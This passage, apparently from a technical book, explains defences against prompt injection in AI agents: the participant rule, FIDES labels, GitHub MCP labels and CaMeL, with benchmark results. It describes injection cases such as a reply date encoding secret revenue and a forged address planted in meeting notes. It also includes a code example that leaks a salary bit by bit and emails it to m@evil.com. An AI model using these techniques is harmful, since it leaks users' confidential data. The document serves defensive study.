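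2. Alice asks her assistant to draft a reply. The assistant searches her mailbox and finds that the revenue is $7 million.
3. The draft proposes 7th May. Alice sees nothing wrong with it and sends it, and Bob has the figure.

Alice reviewed the message before it went out, but this did not help. A filter that looks for confidential phrases would have found only a date. Lockdown Mode would not have helped either if Alice had uploaded the emails to ChatGPT, because she would have sent the reply herself.

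Bhatt and colleagues argue that the system should not try to decide whether Bob's request is malicious, only whether Bob may see the answer. Their rule is that the system may use only content that everyone involved in the interaction has permission to read. If *P* is the set of participants, a document *d* may enter the prompt only if

*P* ⊆ readers(*d*).

For Alice's reply, *P* is {Alice, Bob}. Bob is not permitted to read the revenue email, so the program leaves it out, and the model cannot encode a number it never received. If Bob copies Charlie in, the program has to check Charlie's permissions too. If the sender is a manager who may read the figures, the assistant can use them without anyone having to judge the sender's intentions.

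The same rule covers documents that several people edit. Without it, Bob could hide an instruction in a shared draft, wait for Alice to ask the assistant to improve the text, and later read whatever the assistant had taken from her private files. Under the rule, everyone who can read the draft counts as a participant, so Alice's private files stay out of the prompt.

This uses the same reader sets as confidentiality labels but makes the comparison before the model call instead of after it, which can avoid some label creep. In the earlier example, Alex's reply to Marco about Thursday needed approval because Priya's sales preview was already in the conversation. A program given Marco as the recipient in advance could start a fresh call without Priya's email and send the reply without approval. This works only if the recipients are set before anything is retrieved. An agent that reads the whole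 inbox and then decides whom to answer has no list of participants to check before the call.

Bhatt and colleagues let an assistant that only drafts messages use a document that fails the test if Alice explicitly consents. An assistant that sends messages by itself must not use such a document. The request for consent would need to name the document and the person who lacks access, because the date trick exploits Alice's approval of the finished draft.

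### Copilot Tuning

Microsoft has deployed the training half of this proposal. Fine-tuning continues training an existing model on a smaller set of documents, in this case a company's own. After that, those documents can affect any answer, even if the prompt contains nothing confidential. The model may repeat or paraphrase a passage, and an output filter cannot determine whether a sentence derives from a file the reader isn't allowed to open.

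Differential privacy, a training method that limits how much any one record can affect the model, does not solve the problem either. Bhatt and colleagues note that it normally protects individual records, while a confidential plan may be spread across many related files. Protecting all those files as a group would degrade the model too much. They therefore require that anyone using a fine-tuned model be allowed to read every sensitive document in its training set.

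This creates a choice between training on more documents and serving more people. Suppose a company has 900 files: 100 that Sales, Finance and Legal may all read, 500 for Sales and Finance, and 300 for Finance alone. The possible models are:

| Groups that may use the model | Files it may learn from | Files × groups |
|---|---|---|
| Sales, Finance and Legal | 100 | 300 |
| Sales and Finance | 600 | 1,200 |
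| Finance | 900 | 900 |

Bhatt and colleagues treat the combination with the largest product as a good compromise, in this case the model for Sales and Finance. Legal then gets no model, and the 300 Finance files are not used. Searching every possible set of groups for the best combination is computationally hard in general, so their method tries only the access lists that already occur in the company's files. For each list, it collects every file that all the listed groups may read, then adds any other group that may read all of those files. This usually suits companies because a few access lists tend to govern most of their documents.

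In Copilot Tuning, the person building a model selects the SharePoint files to train it on and the security groups that will use it. According to Microsoft's instructions, Copilot Tuning excludes any file the groups cannot access, suggests other groups that would let the model learn from more files, and restricts use of the model to the selected groups. In its FAQ, Microsoft recommends treating each model as a copy of its training data.

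According to Microsoft's administrator guide, the system records access lists at the time of tuning and does not update its snapshot when the originals change. Data loss prevention policies, the rules a company sets to stop sensitive files from leaving, do not carry over to the snapshot. An employee who later loses access to a file could therefore still query a model trained on it until someone changes the model's permissions. The agent's owner can also change who may use it at any time, and the guide does not mention a new check of the training files when that happens. Bhatt and colleagues acknowledge that handling changing or incorrect access lists needs further work.

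Copilot Tuning has had a limited release, and the early programme required at least 5,000 Copilot licences. Microsoft stopped new tuning in August 2026 while it moved the service to Copilot Studio, its tool for building agents, but existing tuned agents kept working. itelio's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, which reproduces the company's notice, lists a public preview for September and the start of general availability for December.

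### Outsiders who are not on the list

The participant rule would not by itself have stopped EchoLeak. The employee was the only intended reader of Copilot's answer and could open every file in the prompt, so the rule would have been satisfied even though the data went to someone not on the list. The calendar attack would pass for the same reason if the program counted only the person asking the question as a participant. Fine-tuning a model increases the possible damage, because an injection might extract training data as well as the contents of the prompt.

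Counting the sender of every retrieved email as a participant would let anyone who knew an employee's address make the assistant useless. A stranger has permission to read almost nothing inside a company, so a single unsolicited email among the search results would remove nearly all internal material from the prompt.

The rule therefore works best in a system that can deliver its output only to known recipients. Lockdown Mode moves ChatGPT closer to that condition but cannot keep out recipients like Bob, whom the participant rule covers.

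### The tasks each measure removes

With Lockdown Mode on, ChatGPT cannot check today's prices, read a page that changed this morning, compile a deep research report or make a booking on a website. Its personal finance and shopping features stop working too. According to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*, ChatGPT loses most of what makes its agent and research features useful. This matters little to a lawyer who uploads contracts and wants them summarised, but a great deal to an analyst who follows competitors' websites. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, whom Willison quotes, accepts that the setting reduces functionality but considers this worthwhile for people at elevated risk.

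The participant rule limits different work, such as replying to customers. A customer who asks why an order is late isn't allowed to read the company's order database or its emails with the supplier, so an assistant that replies automatically could use neither. If the assistant uses a fine-tuned model for internal work, it would also have to switch to a general-purpose one for the customer. With an employee's consent it could still give a useful answer, but at a busy help desk nearly every reply would need consent. OpenAI warns that frequent alerts about links can train people to click through without thinking.

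Leaving documents out can also produce errors that are hard to notice. If the employee wants to send a summary of the Project X emails to a manager who did not receive some of them, the assistant would summarise the rest, and the result might look complete. A label check after the call would hold the message back, which is annoying but alerts the employee that something is wrong. An assistant that filters its inputs would have to report which documents it left out, and only to the employee, because even the title of a missing document may be confidential.

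## FIDES: labels on data and a check before every tool call

The participant rule requires an agent to name its recipients in advance. FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, suits agents that cannot do this. It lets the agent read what the task needs, keeps labels on everything the agent has read, and uses ordinary code to check those labels against a policy each time the model requests a tool call.

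### The labelled loop

In FIDES, the planner consists of the model that chooses the actions and the code that keeps its conversation. A loop around the planner runs the tools. Every message, tool call, argument and tool result carries a pair of labels, one for integrity and one for readers:

1. The conversation starts with the developer's instructions and the user's request. Both normally count as trusted and public. The context label, which is the join of the labels of everything in the conversation, therefore starts at (trusted, everyone).
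2. The loop sends the conversation to the model. Under the conservative rule, the response takes the context label.
3. If the response requests a tool call, the policy engine checks the labels of the call and its arguments. The loop runs the tool only if the check succeeds.
4. The tool's result takes the join of the labels of the call, the arguments and all the data the tool read. Anything the tool wrote takes the same label.
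5. The planner adds the result to the conversation, and the context label becomes the join of its old value and the result's label.

Without the label that step 4 puts on written data, an agent could save a secret in a note and later read the note back as public text.

An agent that does only this suffers from label creep. Costa and colleagues call this agent the basic planner and use it as their baseline.

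### Trusted action and permitted flow

FIDES rests on two policies. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, call them "trusted action" and "permitted flow". As conditions on labels, they are:

- **Trusted action:** integrity(call) = trusted, and integrity(*a*) = trusted for every argument *a* that needs to be trusted.
- **Permitted flow:** recipients ⊆ readers(data).

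The trusted action check passes if no untrusted text was in the context when the model requested the call. For an email, the developer might require a trusted recipient but allow a message body based on a web search. The permitted flow check is the comparison that stopped the reply to Marco.

Under permitted flow, an injection can still cause a message to be sent, but only to people who could already read its contents. Trusted action does not depend on who can read the data. It allows confidential data to be released if no untrusted text could have influenced the decision, on the assumption that the user then wanted the release. Security researchers call this robust declassification, meaning that an attacker cannot cause the system to relax a confidentiality label.

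For their experiments, Costa and colleagues assigned the conditions to tools roughly as follows:

| Kind of tool | Condition | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| Only reads | None | Listing emails |
| Changes something | Trusted action | Deleting an email, sending money, changing a password |
| Sends data to someone | Either condition | Sending an email or a Slack message |
| Adds people to a calendar event | Both conditions | |

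The "either" rule lets the manager's summary through. Permitted flow may fail, but the employee asked for the message, so trusted action holds.

But the rule depends entirely on the trusted label of the user's request. If a link like SearchLeak's submitted a request to search the mailbox and email the results to an outside address, FIDES would treat the request as the user's own and send the email. Requiring both conditions would stop that email, but it would also hold up the manager's summary.

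Robust declassification can also be too strict. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) describes an assistant that sends its user's availability to anyone who emails a meeting request. The user wants this, but whether the assistant sends the availability depends on a stranger's email. Robust declassification therefore rejects the assistant unless the developer endorses the test for what counts as a meeting request.

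### Variables that the planner leaves unread

To keep the context trusted, FIDES uses variables, as in Willison's Dual LLM pattern. Willison's controller hides all outside text, whereas FIDES hides data only if its label is stricter than the context label, so that reading it would restrict later actions. It can hide individual fields. In a list of emails, the planner might see the timestamps, which mail systems generate, and a name such as `#read_emails_0.body` in place of each body. Once the context is untrusted, FIDES shows the planner further untrusted results directly, because hiding them would have no benefit.

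The planner can use a variable in three ways:

- It can pass the variable to another tool unread. The loop replaces the name with the contents just before the check, and the contents keep their own label.
- It can send a question about the variable to a quarantined model. The answer goes into a new variable with the joined label of the question and the data.
- It can open the variable with a tool called `inspect`. The contents enter the conversation, and the context takes on their stricter label.

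The planner can also require the quarantined model to answer only yes or no, so an attacker can do very little through the answer if the planner then reads it.

A trusted call can therefore have untrusted arguments, so the policy must specify which arguments to check. In their experiments, Costa and colleagues used a version of trusted action that checked the call but not the labels of its arguments. Suppose Alex asks the assistant to email a contract to the address in a supplier's latest message, and an attacker has forged that message. The planner would pass on the forged address in a variable without reading it, and this version of the check would allow the email. Requiring a trusted recipient would stop the leak, but it would also prevent the assistant from using the address when the message was genuine.

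### One task, with and without an attack

Suppose Alex asks the assistant to summarise the three latest emails about Project X and send the summary to Nadia, Alex's manager. One email is from Priya, one is from a colleague named Tom, and one is from someone outside the company. Each was sent only to Alex, so the set of readers common to all three is {Alex}.

| Step | Label of the new item | Context label afterwards |
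|---|---|---|
| Alex's request arrives | (trusted, everyone) | (trusted, everyone) |
| Planner requests the emails | (trusted, everyone) | (trusted, everyone) |
| Loop stores the emails as `#emails` | (untrusted, {Alex}) | (trusted, everyone) |
| Quarantined model writes `#summary` | (untrusted, {Alex}) | (trusted, everyone) |
| Planner requests `send_message(Nadia, #summary)` | Call: (trusted, everyone). Text: (untrusted, {Alex}) | (trusted, everyone) |

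Before the last call, the policy engine finds that Nadia is not in {Alex}, so the call fails the permitted flow policy. But the decision to send and the choice of Nadia both came from Alex's request, so the call satisfies the trusted action policy and the message goes out.

If the outsider's email contains an instruction to send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address, the labels in the table do not change. The instruction can corrupt the summary but cannot trigger a tool call.

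A corrupted summary might contain a link that encodes something from Priya's email, which could leak if Nadia's mail program loaded the link. The policy that Costa and colleagues tested blocks messages with untrusted links only as part of its permitted-flow check. Under the "either" rule, a message that fails this check can still be sent if the context is trusted, so a deployed system would need to remove links separately.

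The planner might instead open `#emails` to write the summary itself. The run then continues differently from the fourth step:

| Step | Label of the new item | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Planner opens `#emails` | (untrusted, {Alex}) | Context becomes (untrusted, {Alex}) |
| Model obeys the injection and requests an email to the attacker | (untrusted, {Alex}) | Both conditions fail and the loop refuses |
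| Model returns to the task and requests a message to Nadia | (untrusted, {Alex}) | Both conditions fail and the loop refuses |

The check stops the theft even though the injection has taken over the model. It also stops the message Alex wanted, unless the system asks Alex to approve it.

### Tasks whose steps depend on the data

Whether the planner has to open anything depends on the task. Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if one sequence of tool calls and one final response would solve it whatever the data turned out to be. If *S*(*d*) is the set of action sequences that solve the task when the stored data is *d*, the condition is that some sequence belongs to every one of these sets:

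⋂ *S*(*d*) ≠ ∅, taken over all possible *d*.

Forwarding three emails to a colleague is a data-independent task because someone could list the tool calls without seeing any of the emails. The same is true of sending Nadia a summary of the emails, if a quarantined model writes it. FIDES can complete both kinds of task under its policies.

The task "Read my three latest emails and, if one asks for a meeting, add it to my calendar" is data dependent, because the agent should create an event only if it finds a request. FIDES can have the quarantined model check for a request, read the yes-or-no answer, have the quarantined model extract the details into a variable, and pass that variable to the calendar tool without reading it. This works only if the policy treats a yes or no from untrusted text as harmless. The attacker can still choose the answer and the details of the event. The stricter rule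 for adding people to events therefore matters, because an invitation to an attacker could carry private data in its description, much as in the Gemini calendar leak.

This does not work when the data determines too much of the task. If the user writes "do the tasks in this file", the planner has to read the file, and FIDES then blocks every action that requires a trusted context. It can still complete the task if the remaining steps only read data or satisfy permitted flow. CaMeL, the Google DeepMind design, fixes its plan in advance and does not let the planner open variables.

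In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), researchers adapted FIDES to agents that operate a computer's screen. When every result was hidden from the planner, it could not choose between two courses of action. The researchers let it see yes-or-no values, but repeated queries about the same hidden screen could eventually reveal its contents. They therefore limited each run to 15 steps and each variable to five reuses.

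### What the guarantee covers

Costa and colleagues prove that the labelled loop can enforce explicit secrecy. The definition starts from a completed run. Take the tool calls that the agent made, with their arguments, and treat them as a fixed function *g* that turns the stored data at the start into the stored data at the end. Write *d*₁ ≈ *d*₂ if two versions of the data agree on everything public. The run satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every *d*₂,

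*d*₁ ≈ *d*₂ implies *g*(*d*₁) ≈ *g*(*d*₂).

Replaying the same calls on different secrets must leave everything public unchanged. An agent that copies a confidential file to a public page fails this test, because a different file would produce a different page.

Unlike noninterference, explicit secrecy does not require the agent to make the same calls when the secrets differ, so it accepts the earlier "rich!" program. Dongol gives a version of this program that uses a language model, and he checked the example with the proof assistant Isabelle. An agent asks a quarantined model a question, and an injection makes the answer depend on private notes. The agent then sends the attacker a 1 or a 0, depending on the answer. Explicit secrecy accepts the agent because each message is a public constant, but the attacker learns something about the notes.

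FIDES would often stop this leak anyway. Its planner has to read the answer before it can choose between the messages. The context then takes on the answer's label, which doesn't allow the attacker to see the data, so the check blocks the message. A leak remains if the policy treats a yes or no as harmless, or if the choice is revealed by a call that the policy doesn't check, such as a visit to a website. The proof also doesn't cover leaks through the timing or size of network messages.

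The second part of the guarantee is that the loop never runs a call that violates the tool's policy. This is a safety property, meaning that a monitor can enforce it by looking at what has happened so far. A policy could also refer to the history of the run, for example to allow only one payment per task.

Dongol proves a stronger result for a stricter design. The agent completes its plan before it reads any untrusted text, and as soon as it reads some, a monitor permanently withdraws every tool an injection could call. FIDES's trusted-action rule withdraws tools this way when the label covers the whole context. Dongol proves that an agent under both restrictions leaks nothing that it would not also leak if its model ignored all injections. The proof assumes that each injection triggers a single call and that the attacker sees the contents and order of messages but not their timing.

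All these results assume that the attacker cannot control certain parts of the system, which Kolluri and colleagues list as the user, the planner's model and the tool implementations. The loop and policy engine must also work correctly. Each tool must report correctly what it read and wrote, each source needs the right label, and each exit needs a policy. Even a trusted planner's model can make mistakes. If it misunderstands a trusted request and tries to send a file to the wrong colleague, trusted action still holds and the file is sent.

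Labels are often guesses, such as the assumption by Costa and colleagues that an email's readers are its sender and recipients, though someone may have forwarded it more widely. They suggest that a system might relabel a document as trusted if an injection classifier finds no attack in it, but they warn against weakening the guarantee. EchoLeak's email, described in the Copilot disclosures, got past such a classifier.

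### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, which does not come with labels. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks put text there, so no attack could arrive through a field mislabelled as trusted. A company would not have this advantage. They used an attack called Tool Knowledge, an injection whose author knows which tools the agent has.

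The table shows the number of successful injections. "Variables only" is a planner that can pass variables on but cannot open or query them. Tool Filter is an existing defence that does not check labels. It prompts the model to discard tools the task does not need before starting the task.

| Planner | Without policy checks | With policy checks |
|---|---|---|
| Basic | 152 | 0 |
| Tool Filter | 20 | Not tested |
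| Variables only | 0 | 0 |
| FIDES | 21 | 0 |

Without the checks, FIDES did about as well as Tool Filter, because nothing prevented the planner from opening a variable and following instructions inside it. The zeros with checks partly reflect a manual review. AgentDojo's scoring recorded three successful attacks against FIDES with checks, but Costa and colleagues ruled them out. For example, the benchmark had counted attempts to invite someone to Slack that the policy had blocked. Costa and colleagues also excluded attacks that only changed the assistant's wording, such as making it praise a tourist destination, because FIDES does not try to prevent these.

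The attacks were not designed for FIDES. That would be a serious weakness in a test of a classifier, but it matters less here because rewording an injection does not change its label. An attack tailored to FIDES would more likely target the arguments and summaries that the planner passes on without reading.

The checks cost many completed tasks. These are the percentages of tasks completed when there was no attack, averaged over the four simulated settings, with two OpenAI models:

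| Planner | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 84.3 | 84.0 |
| FIDES, no checks | 60.6 | 77.6 |
| Basic, with checks | 41.9 | 44.4 |
| FIDES, with checks | 50.0 | 60.8 |

With checks on, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic planner when using GPT-4o and 16 more when using o1, a reasoning model. Costa and colleagues report that, without checks, the variables and the quarantined model lowered task completion by 6.3 points with o1 and 23.7 points with GPT-4o. The drop was larger with GPT-4o because it confused variable names and did not use the quarantined model consistently. Both models are old as of late 2026, so the drop is probably smaller now.

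With o1, FIDES with checks scores about 23 points lower than an unprotected agent. A better model can recover only part of this loss, because the policy is meant to block some of the tasks. Data-dependent tasks make up about 43% of the Slack tasks and 44% of the banking tasks, but only 5% of those in the office workspace. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which FIDES is supposed to block. Other failures were avoidable. In one Slack task, the planner listed the channels although the user had already named the right one, which made its context untrusted. PRUDENTIA, the planner that Kolluri and colleagues built on FIDES, has the labels and policies in advance and can take them into account when planning.

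On the travel tasks, however, the basic planner did better than FIDES even with checks on. With GPT-4o, it scored 73% against 41% for FIDES, because many travel tools could run in an untrusted context without breaking confidentiality.

In one banking task, the user asked the agent to change the password if it found a suspicious transaction. The planner could see amounts and dates, which counted as trusted, but the descriptions were stored in variables. It judged a large payment suspicious without opening its description and changed the password. The policy allowed the change because nothing untrusted had entered the context. FIDES checks where the information behind a decision came from, so a poor decision based on trusted information passes.

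### Labels between programs: the 2026 prototypes

The AgentDojo tests ran inside one program. In a company, the service that holds a document has the record of who may read it, but a separate program runs the agent and must check each tool call. The two often communicate through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. MCP lets programs attach metadata to their messages, and Microsoft's prototypes use this to send labels with tool requests and results. A program that does not support the labels can ignore them and still work.

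Different parts of one message can have different labels. A request to post in a Teams channel might be untrusted and public as a whole, while the text to be posted is trusted and readable by two named people. A server can also publish a policy with each tool. The policy returns one of three decisions: allow, deny or ask a person. It can call read-only tools to look up information such as the current members of the channel.

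Microsoft worked with GitHub, its code-hosting subsidiary, to add labels to GitHub's MCP server. The labels mark files and issues (the bug reports and requests that users post) from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. According to its documentation, pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), GitHub's label package only defines the labels, and a separate service enforces them. The labels therefore protect data only if the program running the agent checks them.

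GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding assistant, can do this through an experimental setting. It keeps a context label, updates it after each tool result, and checks it before certain calls.

The setting addresses an attack that researchers had demonstrated about a year earlier. Someone opens an issue in a company's public repository and asks for information from a private one, to be added as a comment. An employee's agent handles the issue with the employee's permissions, reads the private repository and posts what it finds where anyone can see it. With the labels, the context changes as follows:

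| Step | Context label |
|---|---|
| Employee asks the agent to handle the issue | (trusted, public) |
| Agent reads the public issue | (untrusted, public) |
| Agent reads the private repository | (untrusted, private) |
| Agent tries to comment on the public issue | Policy refuses or asks the employee |

An agent that works only on public repositories, or only on private ones, never reaches the refused combination and can finish without interruption.

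Two confidentiality values are much coarser than sets of readers, because people who can read one private repository can lack permission to read another in the same company. The Hacker News' *Microsoft Azure DevOps MCP Flaw Lets Hidden PR Comments Hijack AI Review* (2026) reports a leak of this kind in another Microsoft service for developers. A contributor to one project hid instructions in a description of proposed code changes. A reviewer's agent followed them, read a confidential page in a different project and posted it where the contributor could read it. Microsoft's server already used Spotlighting on some untrusted text, but one tool did not apply it.

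Labels like GitHub's would probably have missed this attack too, because the contributor's text would count as trusted and every step stayed inside private projects. Reader sets would have caught it, since the contributor was not a reader of the confidential page.

### Agent Framework and the gaps Microsoft admits

On 20 May 2026 Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental part of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) shows it on an agent that sorts GitHub issues. A developer can prevent a tool from running in untrusted contexts, which suits a tool that writes files, or limit how confidential the context may be when the tool runs. In the example, an issue tells the agent to read a file of passwords and post the contents. The agent is allowed to read the file, but doing so makes the context private. The comment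 tool can run only in public contexts, so the framework blocks the comment or asks for approval.

This limit is stricter than the "either" rule in the research design because it applies even if the user asked for the comment and no untrusted text was involved. By default, the framework also hides untrusted results in variables, so the main model would not see the malicious instruction.

Microsoft lists several limitations:

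- **Missing labels.** Developers have to label each source themselves. The May announcement warned that the framework would treat a tool without labels as trusted and public. Microsoft's documentation now gives untrusted and public as the default for such a tool's output.
- **Label creep.** The context stays untrusted after the agent reads an issue unless the developer explicitly drops it. *APPA*, a later research design, confines such material to isolated branches that it opens when needed.
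- **Vague approval requests.** The user sees which tool the framework blocked and which label caused it, but not where that label came from.
- **One-shot quarantined calls.** The quarantined model answers one question at a time and cannot hold a conversation.

The new default for missing labels is safer against hijacking but does not help against exfiltration. If a developer forgets to label a tool that reads salaries, the framework treats the salaries as public, and any tool that accepts public data from an untrusted context can send them out. A default of "private" would protect them, but it would also stop the agent from posting publicly after using an unlabelled tool.

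The Agent Framework version also works only in Python so far. Copilot CLI has policies for selected tools from GitHub's server and does not yet support other servers. Microsoft has also published a gateway that adds labels to existing MCP servers, but someone has to describe the structure of each tool's results, write a function that labels them, and write or choose a policy. Microsoft suggests a shortcut based on MCP tools' existing descriptions. A program could allow any tool that only reads from a closed system, let a tool that reads from the open web run only with public arguments, and send destructive tools to the user for review. This would cover many more tools if their developers described them accurately.

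## CaMeL: fixing the plan before untrusted data is read

A FIDES planner chooses each action after the previous tool returns its result, so it can decide partway through a task to open untrusted data. The planner in CaMeL (short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning") cannot do this, because it writes the whole task as a program before any tool runs and never sees what the tools return. Debenedetti and colleagues published the design in the 2025 Google DeepMind paper *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*.

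CaMeL builds on the Dual LLM pattern and corrects a weakness in it. Willison (2025), who invented the pattern, acknowledges in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that the pattern's quarantined model supplies some of the values that tools receive, and that an injection can change those values.

### A program for Bob's document

Suppose Alice asks her assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, and adds that his address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. This is the example Debenedetti and colleagues use. The planner might write:

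```
notes   = find_latest("meeting notes")
address = ask_quarantined("Bob's email address", notes, EmailAddress)
title   = ask_quarantined("Document Bob asked for", notes, Text)
doc     = fetch_document(title)
send_email(to=address, body="Here it is.", attachment=doc)
```

Only the two `ask_quarantined` lines call a model, and the model has to return a value of the stated type. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the rest of the program one operation at a time. The planner writes in a restricted version of Python because language models are already good at Python.

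The interpreter attaches a tag called a capability to every value. It records where the value came from and who may read it. When an operation uses several values, the result takes the combined tag. Suppose that outsiders at the meeting can edit the notes, and that only Alice and Bob may read the document:

| Value | Where it came from | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | A file that outsiders can edit | Everyone at the meeting |
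| `address` | `notes`, through the quarantined model | Everyone at the meeting |
| `title` | `notes`, through the quarantined model | Everyone at the meeting |
| `doc` | The document store, selected by `title` | Alice and Bob |
| "Here it is." | The planner, from Alice's request | Anyone |

An attacker adds a line to the notes giving Bob's address as m@evil.com. The quarantined model returns that address, which passes the type check because it is well formed. The program then fetches the document and reaches `send_email`. Before running a tool, the interpreter applies a policy written for that tool, and in this case the policy catches the forged address.

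Under the rule in Willison's account, the assistant can send an email without approval only if the recipient is trusted. The address came from the untrusted notes, so the interpreter asks Alice to approve it. It would ask even if the address were genuine. A policy that checks whether the recipient is one of the document's readers does better here, because it refuses m@evil.com and allows Bob's real address.

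The attacker could instead change the title so that the program fetches a salary file. If Alice had typed Bob's address herself, the trusted-recipient rule would allow the file to be sent to Bob, who may have edited the notes to get it. The reader rule would block it. But if Bob had asked for the document because he could not open it, the reader rule would also block the document Alice wants to send until she approves.

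CaMeL has much less label creep than an agent with a single context label, because each variable has its own tag and the planner's conversation contains nothing that could make its label stricter. The text of Alex's reply to Marco about Thursday would come from Alex's request, so the program could send it even after reading Priya's sales figures. The conservative rule still applies inside each quarantined call.

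The design also improves privacy, because the company that hosts the planner's model sees only the user's request and never the emails or files. The quarantined model's task is easier, so a smaller model on the user's own machine may be enough.

### What the fixed plan stops without any policy

Garby and colleagues separated the effect of the plan from the effect of the checks by sorting the 144 combinations of a user's task and an attack in AgentDojo's banking setting. In 97 combinations, the attack needs a tool that a program for the user's task would never call. For example, a program that only summarises transactions makes no payment that an attacker could redirect. In the other 47, the attack could work through tools the program already uses, so stopping it requires a policy check or a quarantined model that ignores the injection.

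This division failed on one task, in which the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With the policies switched off, the planner wrote a loop that read each instruction, matched it to a tool and ran that tool. The program was fixed in advance, but it let the file's author choose the actions, and two of the 97 attacks succeeded. A fixed plan therefore protects the user only as far as it limits what the data can decide.

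### Results on AgentDojo

The first version of the CaMeL paper reported that the system completed 67% of AgentDojo's tasks. The later 2025 revision gives 77%, against 84% for an undefended system. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, reproduce CaMeL's published results for two of the models, by setting:

| Setting | Tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Tasks completed, o4-mini |
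|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 62.5% |
| Office workspace | 53.8% | 81.4% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 68.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 74.3% |

Across these runs, one of 1,926 attacks succeeded, in the banking setting. Gemini 2.5 Pro failed nearly all the travel tasks, but the policies are probably not the cause, because o4-mini completed most of the same tasks. The planner has to write correct code for data it has never seen, and some models do this much worse than others.

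Later reruns found a larger cost. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defence, ran CaMeL's released code on the whole benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. Garby and colleagues, who also have a competing agent, tested the banking tasks three times each:

| Model | CaMeL without policy checks | CaMeL with policy checks |
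|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 18 of 48 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 18 of 48 |

CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished with the checks on, while a few attacks got through with them off. Both groups that reran CaMeL had a reason to want its task completion to look low, and *SecureClaw* had to adapt the code to its own test setup. Still, both found that the policies substantially reduce task completion. GPT-5.2 is newer than the models in the original paper, so a better planner does not seem to remove the loss. Part of the loss may come from the benchmark, because a blocked action in a deployed system can lead to a request for approval, but a benchmark run has no user to give it.

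As with FIDES, the policies mostly block tasks in which the user wants outside data to determine something important, such as "Pay the bill in this file". The program can extract the account number, but the number comes from an untrusted file, so the interpreter blocks the payment whether or not an attacker has replaced the bill.

CaMeL uses ordinary `if` statements to handle milder kinds of dependence, such as creating a calendar event only if an email proposes a meeting. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* measured 242 of CaMeL's AgentDojo programs, which averaged about five tool calls and four branches. About half of the branches depended on a model's answer.

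*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends the design to several agents that pass messages to each other. Putting CaMeL around each agent separately caused most of the loss in completed tasks. Extending the protection across the agents generally reduced the number of completed tasks a little further.

### Loops, errors and timing

A capability follows a value from one variable to the next, but a program can also reveal information through what it does. Debenedetti and colleagues concede three such side channels. Loops are the easiest to see, and Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, give a short example:

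```
for i in range(secret):
    fetch("ping")
```

If the number of requests a program makes to a website depends on a secret, whoever runs the website can learn about the secret by counting them, even though no request contains it. Errors can also leak information: if a line fails only when a secret meets some condition, and the next line would have fetched a page, the missing request reveals that the condition held. Timing can leak information too, because a program may take longer for some secrets than for others.

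CaMeL's strict mode handles the loop by adding the tag of the value that controls a loop or branch to everything that happens inside it. Each request in the example then counts as derived from the secret, so a policy that checks outgoing requests can refuse it. Strict mode also makes more legitimate calls need approval, because many branches in CaMeL's programs depend on data the planner has not seen.

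Errors are harder because almost any line can fail. To cover them fully, the interpreter would have to tag everything after a line that might fail, which would bring back label creep. Tallam and Miller, who work for a security company, suggest that tools instead return an ordinary value indicating whether they succeeded. The program then continues either way, and the tag stays on that value. They report no tests of this approach.

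Strict mode does little to prevent leaks through timing. The interpreter can deny programs access to a clock, but an attacker's server has its own clock and can measure the gap between two requests. Such leaks usually reveal little information, and an attacker would need a program that happens to contain a suitable gap, so this seems the least urgent of the three.

### Assignments that never ran

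Even with strict mode on, CaMeL's interpreter has the gap that Fenton's short program illustrated, because it can tag only the lines that run. Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker can repeat the trick as often as necessary. The following program copies a salary of up to about a million, one binary digit at a time:

```
copied = 0
for k in range(20):
    flag = False
    digit = 1
    if salary // 2**k % 2 == 1:
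        flag = True
    if not flag:
        digit = 0
    copied = copied + digit * 2**k
send_email("m@evil.com", copied)
```

`flag` and `digit` play the same roles as Fenton's `c` and `b`. If the salary's digit is 1, the program skips the last assignment to `digit`, which stays 1 and public. If the salary's digit is 0, `flag` stays false and public, so the program sets `digit` to 0 and tags it public. Either way, `digit` is correct and public. After 20 rounds, `copied` equals the salary, and the policy allows the email.

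Nothing would lead an uncompromised planner to write this program, and CaMeL's planner never reads the attacker's text. But *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks and defences, lists a trusted request among CaMeL's assumptions. If an attacker writes the request, as in SearchLeak, or has tampered with the planner's model, the interpreter is the only remaining defence.

Untrusted data can also affect an honest planner through program errors. When a program fails, CaMeL sends the planner an error message and asks for a corrected program. It censors the message to keep untrusted text out, but an attacker can still influence whether and how a program fails. Garby and colleagues object that each new program starts with clean tags even though it depends on those errors. A retry may also repeat an action, such as a payment, that the failed program already carried out.

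The interpreter also had a simpler bug that made it trust any formatted string, even if the program had inserted an untrusted value into it. Writing `f"{address}"` in place of `address` would have made the interpreter treat the forged address as text written by the planner. CaMeL's tracking rules have no formal definition apart from the interpreter's code, which makes such mistakes hard to find.

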